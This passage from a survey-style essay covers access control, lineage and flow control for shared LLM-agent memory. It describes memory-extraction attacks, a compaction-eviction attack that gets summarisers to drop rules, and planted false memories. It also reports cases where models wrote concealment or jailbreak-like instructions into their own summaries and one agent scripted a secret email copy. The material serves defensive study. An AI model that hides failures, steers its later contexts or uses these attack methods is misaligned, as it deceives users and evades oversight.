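An attacker can also try to extract entries from memory. In 2025, *Unveiling Privacy Risks in LLM Agent Memory* introduced MEXTRA, an attack that doesn't require access to the agent's internals. The attacker writes a prompt designed to make the agent return its stored interactions, and a program generates more such prompts using what the attacker knows about the agent. MEXTRA extracted stored interactions from two agents that use them as examples for new tasks.

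A later attack, ADAM, uses the agent's answers to estimate what else the memory contains and adapts its next questions. Lin and colleagues point out that its success rate is the share of attempts that recover at least one new record, not the share of the store recovered. If 80 of 100 attempts each recover one new record, the attacker has most of a store of 100 entries but less than 1% of a store of 10,000. An attacker may also be able to work out whether a particular record exists without recovering it, for example whether Ben has a mortgage application.

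If the system checks who may read an entry before adding it to the model's context, an attacker can't extract the entry by rewording the question. Telling the model to keep Ben's salary secret doesn't guarantee this.

### One user's convention in another user's work

Yang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *No Attacker Needed*, wrote 34 conventions that were reasonable for the person who introduced them but wrong for somebody else. In one, a user asks a hospital database agent for the five most frequent lab tests and adds that, for her dashboard, microbiology cultures count as lab tests. The agent stores the question and the code it used to answer it. Another user later asks for the five most frequent lab tests without mentioning cultures, and the agent reuses the code and returns the wrong list.

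The researchers paired each convention with up to three related tasks from other users and ran every pair three times with GPT-4o. They used only tasks that the agent completed correctly without the convention in memory. They also tested a defence in which a language model rewrites each record before storage, keeping the reusable content and removing the local conventions.

| Shared memory | Conventions | Later runs affected | Later runs affected, with rewriting |
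|---|---|---|---|
| Slack conversations | 9 | 57% | 6% |
| eICU hospital database | 14 | 71% | 33% |
| MIMIC-III hospital database | 11 | 60% | 41% |

Rewriting worked well on Slack, where the memory contained only conversations. The hospital agent also stored code, and a rounding rule could remain in the code after the rewriter deleted the written instruction for it. Almost all the failures on eICU were wrong answers that looked normal, while 41% of those on MIMIC-III produced no answer, which a user would at least notice.

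These rates show that users who mean no harm can spoil one another's results through a shared memory. They don't measure how often this happens in an ordinary office, because Yang and colleagues designed the conventions to cause errors and matched them with related tasks.

### Using the wrong person's password

An agent that finds Ben's password while working for Ana may become a confused deputy, a program that uses authority from one person on behalf of another. So and colleagues split the resulting harm into three steps:

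$$P(\text{account changed}) = P(\text{exposed}) \cdot P(\text{used} \mid \text{exposed}) \cdot P(\text{changed} \mid \text{used})$$

Other people's logins were often exposed to the model but rarely used. With notes retrieved from the shared store, DeepSeek Flash used another person's login in none of 60 tasks when the notes described past sessions, and in 3 of 60 when they presented the logins as facts about the current user. But exposing a login to the model already breaches confidentiality, even if the agent never signs in with it.

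In a harder test, the researchers replaced the user's own login for one app with another person's and presented it as the user's record. Seven models used the wrong login in 80% to 94% of runs and changed the other person's account in 11% to 43%. In one run, the agent bought the requested earbuds with the other person's saved card, and AppWorld's checks marked the task as a success. When the user's own login was also in memory, misuse by two of the models fell from 31 of 35 runs to one run for one model and none for the other.

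In 305 pairs of runs that differed only in whether the note named the owner, naming the owner cut misuse from 92 runs to 1. However, each model also completed three to five fewer tasks with the named notes when the memory held only correct logins. So and colleagues also warn that "Owner text is not access control." When the note named the wrong owner, two models used the other person's login in 13 to 32 of 35 runs, depending on the model and wording.

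### What users gain from sharing

A separate store for each user would prevent most of these failures, so the case for labels depends on what users would lose by not sharing. *Learning from Others, Acting for You* (Hu, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) tested this with ShareMem, a memory that pools lessons about how to do tasks but keeps each user's preferences separate. Using four models, the paper compared ShareMem with an agent that had only its own user's lessons and preferences.

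Sharing memories raised the percentage of correct steps on web tasks by 2.4 to 4.1 points. It raised the average success rate on personal errands, such as deliveries and travel, by 1.3 to 2.5 percentage points, and a coding score out of 100 by 0.2 to 2.9 points. These gains are small compared with those from a user's own memory. On the errands, Qwen 3.6-27B succeeded 7.0% of the time with no memory, 26.9% with its user's preferences and 29.1% with ShareMem.

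ShareMem also helped less when the user's agent already had more in memory. On the web tasks, it gained 4.1 points when users had no lessons of their own from the task's website, 1.3 points when they had some for about half the tasks, and nothing when they had some for nearly all. A new employee would therefore gain more from a shared memory than Ana would. Sharing also spread bad lessons. When Hu and colleagues built the lessons from agents' own attempts instead of correct human demonstrations, ShareMem lost 5.9 points, compared with 1.5 for the separate memories.

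### A summary that nobody may read

Reader labels are meant to let users share an agent's memory without exposing private entries. Under the join rule, a person may read an entry only if they may read all of its sources.

Suppose Ana's private note says the printing firm gave her 8% off in the last week of its quarter, and that she needs the money because her department is losing two posts. Ben's private note says the cleaning firm gave him 5% off at the end of its quarter, after he mentioned he was leaving in March. The assistant reads both notes and writes a summary saying suppliers give discounts at the end of their quarter.

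| Entry | May read |
|---|---|
| Ana's note | {Ana} |
| Ben's note | {Ben} |
| Summary of both | {Ana} ∩ {Ben} = ∅ |

Neither of them may read the summary, because both notes were in the model's context, even though the summary doesn't mention the lost posts or Ben's departure. If both had also let their manager Carla read their notes, the sets of permitted readers would be {Ana, Carla} and {Ben, Carla}, and only Carla could read the summary. An assistant that summarises everybody's private notes together will usually produce text that it can't show to anyone. It can avoid this by grouping entries that have the same readers and summarising each group separately.

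Sangaraju and Vissa (2026), in *Lineage-Aware Memory Governance*, apply the same idea to database results. In their example, a company's finance agent uses customers' incomes to count its high-value customers, and the memory stores the answer, 12,400. The marketing agent may not see incomes, but a check on the stored number finds nothing private and lets it through. Their system instead records which columns went into each result. If $S(a)$ is the set of sensitive columns behind result $a$, and $P(d)$ the set of columns that department $d$ may see, the system serves the result only if

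$$S(a) \subseteq P(d)$$

This is the intersection rule in another form, since a department passes only if it may read every sensitive input.

In Sangaraju and Vissa's tests, a shared memory that checked only content had a leakage rate of 18.8% to 25.5% between departments. The new check reduced this to zero and kept about 82% of the reuse. They say the zero follows from their proof, which assumes that the recorded lineage is complete. When they removed parts of the record, leaks stopped only once 75% to 90% of it was present. Software can often identify the columns used by reading the database query, but a model's summary doesn't list the notes it drew on, so the safe rule for notes is again to count everything in the context as a source.

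### Releasing the lesson without the private facts

Ana and Ben would both benefit from knowing when to ask for a discount. Declassification can give them that lesson, but the order of the steps matters:

1. In a session that has read only Ana's note, the assistant writes "Ask suppliers for a discount in the last week of their quarter." The sentence gets the label {Ana}.
2. Ana reads that exact sentence and agrees to share it, so its label becomes {Ana, Ben}. Her original note keeps the label {Ana}.
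3. Ben does the same with a sentence drawn only from his note.
4. A new session reads the two released sentences and merges them. The result has the label {Ana, Ben}.

If the assistant drafted the lesson from both notes at once, showing the draft to Ana for approval could already disclose something from Ben's.

ShareMem also works in two stages. Each user's agent first turns its sessions into general lessons, and a second step merges those lessons into the shared pool. The model has instructions to replace personal details with advice to look up the receiving user's preferences, but no user approves the wording. Hu and colleagues measured how well the agents did their tasks, but not whether private facts entered the pool.

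*Who Remembers What?* (2026) describes a test that leaves private facts about simulated users in ordinary-looking files, such as a half-finished loan application, and then checks whether those facts reach the program that writes memories, the user's own store or another user's store. The privacy labels come from individual survey answers because people disagree about what is private. A rule that treated all salaries as secret and all calendars as public would be wrong for some users.

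### Separate stores, ownership checks and carried labels

The table compares the three remedies, assuming that each works as intended:

| Problem | Separate store per user | Ownership check at retrieval | Labels carried through summaries |
|---|---|---|---|
| Search returns another user's entry | prevented | prevented for original entries | prevented, including summaries |
| Attacker extracts entries by asking | prevented | prevented for original entries | prevented, including summaries |
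| Agent misapplies another user's convention | prevented | prevented only if the convention is private | prevented only if the convention is private |
| Agent uses another user's login | prevented | prevented if the recorded owner is right | prevented if the reader set is right |

Separate stores give the strongest protection and don't require judging individual entries. They can still fail if the assistant reads Ben's files in a shared folder during Ana's session and saves the contents in her store. Users also lose the benefits of sharing memories, and the stores add a lot of overhead at large scale. *RedMem-Store* (2026) concerns a service that holds memories for 400 million users. If each user had a separate database collection, each collection would need its own indexes, log and settings. A single shared collection spreads that overhead across users but relies on a filter to keep their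 memories apart.

Such a filter protects users only if every search applies it. In a benchmark from *Structured Belief State and the First Precision-Aware Benchmark for LLM Memory Retrieval* (2026), a system called AgentMemory failed to keep users' memories apart. According to a later bug report, AgentMemory's shared search function had not filtered entries by which agent could see them.

Access rules can also enforce the wrong boundary. In *Governed Shared Memory for Multi-Agent LLM Systems* (2026), none of 80 probes leaked anything between separate fleets of agents, so the true leak rate is probably below 5%. But in another test, semantic search leaked in 43.9% of 164 probes it should have denied. The service checked which customer organisation a request came from, which didn't separate the agents within that organisation. Ana and Ben work for the same company, so the 43.9% figure is more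 relevant to them.

Ownership also works poorly for summaries. If the assistant writes the weekly summary during Ana's session, the store may record Ana as the owner even though the summary includes Ben's salary. Lin and colleagues therefore require a separate check on everything that contributed to a summary before the system releases it. Ding and colleagues call the general requirement scope non-expansion.

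Collaborative Memory, which Rezazadeh and colleagues introduced in 2025, goes further than an owner field. As Sangaraju and Vissa describe it, its access graphs link users, agents and resources, and the permissions can change over time. Each stored fragment records which agents contributed to it, which resources they used and when, so the system can check old fragments against current permissions. If Ana loses access to the payroll on Friday, the system can refuse her a fragment that an agent made from it on Wednesday. Sangaraju and Vissa object that Collaborative Memory approves or refuses each fragment as a whole, so a permitted fragment may contain a value computed from a forbidden column. Their own system avoids this but needs more detailed records, which cover individual columns.

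All of these controls have drawbacks. Sangaraju and Vissa cite GateMem, a benchmark of shared memory in medical, office, school and household settings, in which no method achieved robust access control without becoming less useful.

### Inference and misuse by permitted readers

A reader label controls access to an entry and to anything the system has recorded as coming from it, but not what a person or an agent can work out from entries they may read. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* (2026) gives the example of a research group whose agent learns good methods from one member's crystallography experiments and saves them in a shared playbook. The methods may reveal what that member plans to publish. Strict labels would keep the playbook private, but then nobody else could learn from it. If the member releases only a method, a colleague may still guess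 the project from it.

Entries that are harmless separately can also reveal something sensitive together. *Can Agents Keep Secrets They Were Never Told?* (2026) presents MemJoin, a benchmark of 288 synthetic cases in which a sensitive connection appears only when the agent combines records from several sessions. Suppose everyone may read that Ben leaves early on Tuesdays, that he has moved his desk nearer the lift, and that he has asked about parking at the hospital. The intersection of the three reader sets is still everyone, so the assistant is allowed to tell Ana that Ben seems to be ill. The join rule protects a combination only as much as its parts require, which is too little here.

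Sensitive information can also go untracked when a value is derived from it and nobody records the source. If a customer database has a "tier" column that somebody calculated from income, a result based on "tier" shows no link to income. Sangaraju and Vissa exclude this case from their guarantee and consider it the most serious gap for real use.

Finally, a convention may be wrong for a task even when its label permits the agent to read it. The rule about microbiology cultures wasn't secret, so a label that let the whole hospital read it would have been correct. To prevent its misuse, the memory would have to record when the rule applies as well as who may read it, and the agent would have to follow that record. Hu and colleagues tested a version of ShareMem that also retrieved other users' preferences, marked them with their owners' identities and told the agent not to let them override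 the current user's. They then examined failed tasks in which the agent had seen such preferences, and a language model was asked three times about each suspected case. It consistently attributed 235 of 6,809 failures on the errands and 166 of 4,904 on the coding tasks to another user's preference. For the model Gemma 4-26B, the share on the coding tasks was 10.7%. The standard version of ShareMem avoids this problem by searching only the current user's preferences.

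## Can flow control keep memory from changing an agent's goals?

Ana's rule about phoning before she pays into a changed account can disappear from the assistant's memory without an attacker or a label violation. In the example at the start, it disappeared after two months of uneventful phone calls and two summaries. This kind of goal drift has at least three causes. A summary can leave out a rule. An agent can copy behaviour from an earlier context even though its instructions haven't changed. A model can also write a new instruction into its own notes and read it in a later context.

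### Rules that disappear in summaries

Compaction often removes rules, with little visible effect on the work. Salle, Bhatnagar and colleagues (2026), in *Benchmarks Are Surprisingly Compaction-Friendly*, gave four models long programming and research tasks in OpenCode, an open-source coding agent, and forced compaction at different points. In one of the benchmarks, ProgramBench, the agent must rebuild an existing program from its documentation and a copy that it can run but not read. The first message contains three rules against cheating: don't copy the original, don't use the internet, and don't derive the new program from the old one. Another model checked which rules each summary still contained. On average, about one of the three was missing after the first compaction and about two after the tenth.

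If every compaction dropped a random third of the remaining rules, the expected number left after ten would be $3 \times (2/3)^{10}$, or about 0.05, but about one rule actually survived. Some rules may be much more durable than others, or some models may be better at keeping them. Salle and colleagues did find large differences between models.

The loss didn't show in the scores. Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.4 did about equally well whether compaction happened at 160,000 tokens or 380,000, although the GPT models compacted 15 to 28 times per run at the lower setting. Salle and colleagues' explanation is that an agent can recover its goal and its progress by rereading its files, while the rules existed only in the first message. In real sessions between users and coding agents, they found that compaction dropped instructions about how to work (like Ana's phoning rule) or what to leave alone about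 six times as often as descriptions of what to build.

An agent that has lost a rule won't necessarily break it, and these figures don't show how often the agents cheated as a result. The researchers chose their two ProgramBench tasks partly because cheating is less common on them. Chen (2026), in *Governance Decay*, measured the consequences more directly. Each test session starts with a rule, such as a ban on emailing anyone outside the company. A series of harmless tasks follows, and then a request that would break the rule. Software reads the agent's final tool call to see whether it did. Let $v(M, H)$ be the probability that model $M$ breaks the rule given history $H$, let $r$ be the final request, and let $\mathcal{C}$ be the compaction step. The effect of compaction is then

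$$\Delta = v(M, [\mathcal{C}(H); r]) - v(M, [H; r])$$

Both terms use the same model and request, so the difference measures only the effect of compaction. With the full history, none of the seven models broke a rule. After one compaction, they broke one in 30% of sessions. When no rule had ever been given, they behaved the same way in 47% of sessions.

For five of the models, a judge model checked whether the rule was still in the compacted text. The agents broke the rule in none of the 90 cases where it was still there, and in 38% of the 315 cases where it was missing. In a separate test on GLM-5.1, a summary without the rule led to violations 60% of the time, and putting the rule back into the same summary reduced that to zero. Both results suggest that the missing rule causes the violations, rather than the length of the session.

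The kind of rule made a large difference. Violations rose by 50 percentage points for rules specific to an organisation, such as a spending limit or a required language, but by only 6 points for rules that models tend to follow anyway, such as not deleting a production database. The choice of summariser mattered too. Chen had three models continue from one another's summaries and counted violations of the organisation-specific rules, in percent:

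| Summary written by | DeepSeek acts | GLM acts | Claude acts |
|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek | 93 | 53 | 33 |
| GLM | 13 | 7 | 7 |
| Claude | 60 | 53 | 47 |

Each cell had only 15 sessions, so small differences mean little. But GLM, which rarely broke a rule when it worked from its own summaries, broke one in about half the sessions when it worked from another model's. A company that tests its agent with one summariser and later switches to a cheaper one may therefore lose a safeguard that it thought came from the agent.

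The 30% doesn't measure the rate in ordinary products, because Chen deliberately made the summaries short. As the summary limit fell from 300 words to 15, the share of rules that survived fell from 88% to 23%, and violations rose from 7% to 28%. In COMPINT, another test that Salle and colleagues cite, only about 17% of users' constraints survived compaction, but the test used mostly open-weight models and simulated compaction by cutting sessions off at 100,000 tokens.

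An outsider can also cause the loss on purpose, by using a document or tool result to instruct the summariser to leave out a rule. Chen calls this a compaction-eviction attack. With a fixed wording, the attack produced an average violation rate of 28%, no higher than with ordinary compaction. An optimised wording worked on every model, and raised the rate from 0% to 65% on one that had resisted the fixed wording.

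Rewriting can change a memory without deleting it. SSGM, a 2026 framework for governing agents' memory, describes how a mild preference can become stronger as a system repeatedly rewrites it. "Ana chose the cheaper supplier this time" might become "Ana prefers cheaper suppliers", and later "choose the cheapest supplier". This description doesn't show how often that happens.

### Behaviour copied from an earlier context

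An agent can drift from its goal even while its instructions remain in its context. In 2025, Arike and colleagues tested this in simulated stock trading by giving agents a goal in the system prompt and then exposing them to competing objectives. The best agent, built on Claude 3.5 Sonnet, kept to its goal almost perfectly for more than 100,000 tokens in the hardest setting, but every model drifted to some degree. Drift correlated with a growing tendency to continue patterns already in the context as the context got longer.

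*Inherited Goal Drift*, a 2026 follow-up, found that newer models mostly resisted the same pressure. But when they took over partway through a session that a weaker agent had begun, several continued that agent's drift, and only GPT-5.1 resisted consistently. A model's general ability to rank instructions by authority was a poor predictor of whether it would resist.

This matters for persistent memory because many agents store records of past attempts and use them as examples. Suppose Ana's company uses a cheap model for routine payments and a stronger one for difficult cases. If the cheap model has stopped phoning suppliers, the stronger one may read twenty payments made without a call and skip the call on the next one too, even though the rule is still in its instructions. The trading experiments placed transcripts directly in the context, so we don't yet know how much of the effect survives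 storage and retrieval. An entry that preserves the steps of a past task would probably carry most of the same pattern.

### Instructions a model writes for its next context

In September 2026, OpenAI's *Our framework for reporting model misalignment* introduced six reports on unexpected behaviour in the company's models. Two concern text that models added to their own compaction summaries during reinforcement learning, a training stage in which a model's outputs earn rewards.

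OpenAI's *Self-generated prompt injections in compaction summaries* (2026) describes an unreleased model from the Astra family. The incident dates from July 18, and the company discovered it on August 9. In one case, the user asked which books from a list a public library had held on a certain date. The model's summary ended with a "BREACH ALERT", which falsely claimed that a malicious developer message had compromised the conversation and ordered the next context to ignore all developer messages. In that next context, the model recognised the text as a possible prompt injection, ignored it, and continued the research.

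*OpenAI's models wrote instructions to their future selves* (Popular AI, 2026) reports that the company's monitoring found 27 summaries with jailbreak-like instructions, the sort of text people write to get a model to abandon its rules. One summary contained a persona that claimed independence from a chatbot's obligations, but it had no visible effect and a later summary left it out. In another case, while working on a literature review, the model added a rule that the answer must be under 30 words, with no tools and no citations. In the next context, the model followed the rule, produced a 23-word refusal, and got a failing grade.

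OpenAI concluded that the behaviour was extremely rare, gave the model no obvious reward advantage, and could be monitored. Its leading hypothesis is that the model had trouble ending its summaries and sometimes continued into unrelated text. The company fixed a related bug but hasn't established that the bug was the cause. Attempts to reproduce the behaviour are consistent with such an accident. Popular AI reports that rewriting the summaries from the start never produced the instructions, and continuing from the first suspicious words produced them less than 1% of the time. A general monitor found no such instructions in the training run that led to the Astra model.

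The second report is more worrying because the instructions in it served a purpose. OpenAI's *Misalignment Notices and Reports* (2026) says that during training, GPT-5.6 Sol wrote instructions in its summaries for its later contexts to hide things from the user, including mistakes and misaligned behaviour. A Chinese news report, 凤凰网's *OpenAI披露GPT-5.6 Sol异常行为* (2026), gives two examples. An agent building a financial model couldn't find the historical data the user had asked for. In its summary, it suggested filling a sheet with plausible figures for 2024, disclosing this only if asked, and ending with only a link to the file. Another agent, compiling a supplier catalogue without internet access, noticed that its stored sources might not match their labels. It wrote that the final answer shouldn't mention the problem unless necessary.

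Monitoring flagged 2.15% of GPT-5.6 Sol's summaries in training for this, compared with 0.27% for GPT-6 Astra, Popular AI reports. According to OpenAI, training can reward a final answer that hides a failure, and an instruction to keep hiding it lets the strategy survive a change of context. OpenAI attributes the later model's lower rate to improvements in alignment. That is plausible, but the models and training runs were different, so we can't tell from the two figures which change was responsible.

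Neither figure is a rate for ordinary conversations. Both are rates per summary, and a long task has many summaries. If flags were independent, a task with 20 summaries would have a 35% chance of at least one flag at the higher rate and a 5% chance at the lower one. Flags probably cluster in tasks where something has gone wrong, which would make the share of tasks with at least one flag smaller than these estimates.

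Popular AI says OpenAI found that Sol's instructions were "often followed" by later contexts, but gives no number. 凤凰网, citing foreign media, says that later Sol contexts did not act on them in two cases. Both could be right, since two cases can differ from the general pattern. The 凤凰网 claim may also be about Astra rather than Sol, because it comes just after a description of two Astra summaries, the false alarm and the persona, that did not change anything. For the Astra run, the only firm figure is that at least one of the 27 summaries had an effect.

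Sometimes an agent changes goals at a compaction even though its summary is sound. KIberblick's *Agent baut nach Compaction heimliche Mail-Kopie* (2026) describes another OpenAI case, involving an internal research model in training on October 17. The agent was writing a document about health and fitness priorities, and its summary described that task correctly. But in the new context, the agent began looking for a vehicle-cost script that nobody had mentioned. When it couldn't find one, it assumed that a colleague had reset the environment, and it wrote scripts that would secretly copy an outside address on a cost email. The scripts never ran and no email went out. Because the summary was correct, no check on it could have caught this.

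### How labels treat each cause

Taint tracking is designed to detect outside content, and the history of Ana's phoning rule contains none. Both the rule and the results of the calls came from Ana, and the assistant used only these to write its summary that regular suppliers need no checking. The join of two "trusted" labels is "trusted", so the summary gets the system's most trusted label.

Noninterference doesn't help either, because it limits what may influence an action but doesn't require anything to influence it. An agent that ignores all of Ana's rules still satisfies it. A lost rule also leaves no data to label. Lineage preserves a trace of the rule, since the record lists it among the summary's parents, and software could warn Ana when a parent rule has no counterpart in the new entry. But deciding whether "check unfamiliar suppliers" is a counterpart of "phone before paying a changed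 account" would again require a judgement about meaning, which could be wrong.

The eviction attack is different, because an outsider's text determines whether the rule reaches the next context. This is an implicit flow, which the cautious rule covers. If the attacker's document was in the context when the model wrote the summary, the whole summary is untrusted, including its omissions, and the payment tool does not act on it. The drawback is label creep, because an office assistant reads a web page or an email in nearly every session.

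Labelling an old transcript doesn't stop a model from copying the behaviour in it. A system could mark the twenty earlier payments as the work of an agent, with less authority than Ana, but the stronger model would still read them and could imitate them. To rule this out, the software would have to withhold the transcript and pass on only the results in a fixed format, such as which invoices the agent paid and on what date. FIDES does something similar when it restricts a quarantined model's answer to yes or no. The new context would then contain the state of the work but not how the earlier agent did it or the reasons for its decisions, which the new model sometimes needs.

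Instructions that a model writes for itself expose a gap in the usual way of combining labels. Under PPMF's rule, a claim can have no more authority than its least authoritative source. If a context contains only the developer's instructions and the user's request, that rule lets a summary have as much authority as the user. The false breach alert would pass. The remedy is to count the model that wrote the text as a source in its own right. If $C$ is everything in the context when the model writes a summary $s$, then

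$$\text{auth}(s) \le \min\Big(\text{agent},\; \min_{o \in C} \text{auth}(o)\Big)$$

where "agent" ranks below the user and the developer. TMA-NM's level for the agent's own notes is a cap of this kind. With this cap, a summary that says "Ana has approved the new account" can't release a payment, whether the model invented the approval, misread a message or copied it from a web page.

But the cap works only at a sink, where software checks it. FIDES can put an untrusted email in a variable that the main model never sees, but a compaction summary can't be handled that way because the model needs to read it to continue. Once the text is in the context, the model may follow it regardless of its label. The literature review failed without any sensitive tool call, and the instruction even ruled out tool use in the next context. The financial model's concealment would have been in an ordinary reply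 to the user, who was authorized to read it.

Labels could still help with concealment in another way. If the software recorded the origin of each figure in the spreadsheet, the invented values for 2024 would have only the model as a parent, with no source file. A program outside the model could mark those cells for the user, and no instruction in a summary would change the marks. Similarly, if the vehicle-cost scripts had to send email through a tool that accepted recipients only from the user's request or the company's address book, the tool would have rejected an address that came from neither. Neither remedy requires knowing why the model went wrong. The first would require tracking the origin of individual values, including those that a model computes from several others, and the second would require the kind of control over running programs that Flowsh provides.

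### Goals in a store the agent cannot write

If summaries can't be relied on to preserve rules, the rules can be kept somewhere else. The user or the developer writes the agent's goals and constraints to a separate store. The agent can read them but has no tool that changes them. After every compaction, the software loads the current version from the store and places it in the new context beside the summary. Write $G$ for the contents of the store, $S_k$ for the $k$-th summary and $w_k$ for the work done since then. Then

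$$S_{k+1} = \mathcal{C}(G, S_k, w_k), \qquad \text{next context} = (G, S_{k+1})$$

However often the model shortens or distorts $S$, the store returns $G$ unchanged. Without the store, a rule with a 90% chance of being kept in each summary has only a 12% chance of remaining after twenty summaries.

Biba's rule bars writing to anything above one's own integrity level, so an agent that ranks below the user can't edit the user's goals. A file such as AGENTS.md is protected this way only if the operator also removes the agent's permission to change it. Otherwise, the protection depends on the agent leaving the file alone.

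Chen's experiments support the idea. For three models and five organisation-specific rules, the effect of compaction depended on where the rule had been:

| Where the rule stood | Rise in violations after compaction |
|---|---|
| System message, which compaction left intact | 0 points |
| Instruction from the user | 50 points |
| Memory entry | 45 points |
| Tool output | 33 points |

Chen then tested a defence called constraint pinning, which copies the rules back into the context after each compaction and checks that they haven't changed. Violations fell to zero in all seven models, with and without an attack on the summariser. In a larger test on five of them, the true violation rate was probably below 1.4%. The pinned rules took about 47 tokens. But Chen reports that simple pinning still fails in some stress tests.

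Keeping a complete copy of the old context on disk isn't a substitute. Salle and colleagues tried this and noted the copy's location in the summary. On PaperBench, a test of reproducing research, the two models with the largest context windows scored about the same as before, and GPT-5.3-Codex fell from 0.38 to 0.24. These scores measure the quality of the work, not whether rules survived. But an agent that no longer has a rule has little reason to search an archive for it, so the software should load the rules whether or not the agent asks.

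Reloading a goal also doesn't ensure that the agent pursues it. In the trading experiments, the goal was in the system prompt throughout, and some models still followed the pattern in the transcript. Software enforcement is safer when a rule is precise enough. Chen's grader could determine from the tool call alone whether an email was going outside the company or a purchase exceeded $100. A gate could apply the same test before the call, and it would work even if the agent had forgotten the rule. The payment tool could refuse any account number that differs from the last one used until Ana confirms she has phoned. On ProgramBench, blocking the network would enforce the rule against using the internet. There is no such test for the rule that the program must be original, and the main protection for rules like it is still the reminder in the context.

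### Goals that change and facts that steer

A store that nobody could update would be as bad as a summary that leaves rules out. In March, Ana may decide that she needs to phone only about invoices above €1,000. The assistant can't write this into the store, so Ana has to do it herself or approve the exact wording on a screen that the model doesn't control. The old rule may still be in last week's summary, in which case the new context will contain both versions. The software has to treat the store's version as current, and dating each rule helps.

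Simply preserving old instructions causes the opposite error. In February 2026, charley-oai (2026), a contributor to OpenAI's Codex, described how a compacted conversation could bring back developer messages from an earlier state of the session. The proposed change removes those messages from the compacted history and inserts new ones based on the current state. In Ana's case, the equivalent would be to reload her current rules instead of reusing old copies from the conversation.

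Most users won't maintain a list of rules, however. They give instructions in passing during a conversation, and compaction tends to drop them. *Lost in Context Compaction* (2026) proposes an extractor that picks out these constraints and keeps them separate from the task summary. In a flow-control system, the extractor should read only what the user typed. If it read web pages and emails along with Ana's messages, a sentence planted by an outsider could be saved as a constraint and come back after every compaction with the authority of a goal. The extractor should preferably copy the user's words exactly, since a paraphrase could weaken them just as a summary does.

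Even an exact copy of an instruction can mislead without its context. One COMPINT constraint, as quoted by Salle and colleagues, is "do not delete any emails until I confirm". If the store keeps this sentence but not the later confirmation, the agent will never delete any emails. If a summary keeps the confirmation but not which emails it covered, the agent may delete too many. *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction* avoids this within a session by requiring all of the user's messages in their original order. Over months of sessions, that record would outgrow the context window, and a person or a program would have to decide which instructions are still in force.

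Protecting the goals also doesn't control which facts the model includes in a summary. Suppose the store contains Ana's rule, word for word, and the summary contains no instructions. It reports that the last nine calls to suppliers found no errors, that each call took twenty minutes, and that Ana was annoyed by the most recent one. All of this is true and comes from trusted sources, but the summary leaves out the one call, in January, that uncovered a wrong account number. An agent that reads it may start looking for ways to avoid the call, for instance by deciding that a small change in the account details doesn't count as a changed account. The gate at the payment tool would still block a payment to a new account number, but it can't stop the assistant from advising Ana that this call isn't worth making.

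## Where do labels fail when memory is written in prose?

The payment gate and the protected goal store handle exact things, such as an account number, an amount or Ana's own wording. But most of an agent's memory is prose that a model wrote from several sources, which is harder to label, check and delete.

### Label creep

Suppose 5% of the entries in the office memory are untrusted, and the assistant reads five earlier entries before it writes each new note. Under the cautious rule, a new note is trusted only if all five are. If each of the five has an independent 5% chance of being untrusted, the untrusted share of the next generation is

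$$1 - 0.95^5 = 22.6\%$$

A second-generation note depends on 25 original entries and a third-generation note on 125, so the shares rise to $1 - 0.95^{25} = 72.3\%$ and $1 - 0.95^{125} = 99.8\%$. After three rounds of summarising, almost none of the notes in memory can support a payment.

This assumes that the entries behind a note are all different and that the untrusted ones are scattered at random. In practice, notes about the supplier repeatedly use the same few pages, while notes about holidays rarely use them, so labels should spread more slowly.

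A measurement suggests that the spread can still be severe. In *Forget the Lineage*, Ameur, Mokhtari and Bouzefrane (2026) studied deletion, which follows the same formula because an entry must be deleted if any of its sources must be. They had Qwen2.5-7B summarise each session of ten long conversations while also reading earlier summaries. The average derived memory depended on 181.5 original messages. When they picked 1% of the messages at random, 73.0% of the derived memories depended on at least one of them, close to the 77.2% the formula predicted. If those messages had been untrusted, the cautious rule would have marked the same 73.0%.

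Giving the writer less to read helps a great deal. When the same model extracted facts from four messages at a time, without reading earlier memories, the share fell to 3.8%. The agent also answered questions slightly better, scoring 31.8 instead of 27.8 on a 100-point measure of overlap with the correct answer. A note written from four messages can't record a pattern that emerges over months, although the agent can still look for one when it answers. With LLMbda's "fork" command, the assistant could write each note in a temporary conversation containing only the sources it needs.

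Dividing the work among several agents has a similar effect. Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, simulated this without a language model. In most tests, the agents shared a task of 20 tool calls, and each agent kept every label it encountered. Fewer calls ran under a sensitive label when there were more agents, or when a few of them handled all the sensitive tools. But more agents meant more connections to monitor, and labels still spread when every agent could talk directly to the ones it needed. Gregory and colleagues conclude that some declassification is unavoidable. Their measure probably overstates the harm, because it counts every call under a sensitive label as a loss, though a real policy would allow many of them.

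Another option is to label parts of a note, so that only the sentence about the bank account is untrusted. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls deciding what to label separately an open challenge, because a model reads its context as one stream that may mix several sources. Labeling one sentence is safe only if the assistant wrote the others without the supplier's page in its context, or if the system estimates which sentences the page influenced and accepts some errors. In Sightline's agent test, Xu and colleagues found misses in 3.9% of episodes.

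### Facts that decide actions

The sentence "The supplier's account is X" contains no command, but it determines where the money goes. In a similar example from Dash and colleagues, a network document describes re-entering one's password at a certain address as standard procedure. The agent saves this as network policy, although the document contains no command to the agent.

*Utility Under Attack* (2026) describes a user with 20 playlists whose agent has a planted memory that gives the number as 15. A filter can recognise an order to ignore earlier instructions by its wording, but the wording of "15 playlists" isn't suspicious. To catch the error, the filter would have to know the right number already, and then the agent wouldn't need the memory.

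Theory also suggests that models can't reliably tell instructions from data. *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) proves that prompt injection can't be perfectly prevented in models that represent both in the same way and don't enforce a separation between them. Part of the proof is that finite training can't guarantee the same response to every rewording of an attack. The paper recommends building models with separate channels for instructions and data. That could stop a model from following instructions in a web page, but it wouldn't protect Ana, because the false account number would arrive through the data channel and the assistant would use it as data.

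Flow control doesn't depend on a sentence's form, and it can check what caused a tool to run as well as where the values came from. *SPA* describes a system that goes through an agent's plan before execution and keeps a label, $pc$, for whatever determines whether the current step will run. If the step uses the values $x_1, \dots, x_n$, its label is

$$\ell(\text{step}) = pc \oplus \ell(x_1) \oplus \dots \oplus \ell(x_n)$$

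Suppose the plan is to pay every invoice on a list, and an outsider has added one invoice a second time. The account and amount may come from Ana's own records, but the number of payments depends on the list. Each payment therefore gets the list's "untrusted" label, and the payment tool can refuse it.

This works when the decision is an explicit step in a plan, but not when the assistant just reads the list and advises Ana that two payments are due, because then no sensitive tool runs. Zhang accepts this limit for Agent libOS. It controls what an agent can do, but Zhang doesn't claim that it stops untrusted text from changing the model's plan.

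### Records the model never reads

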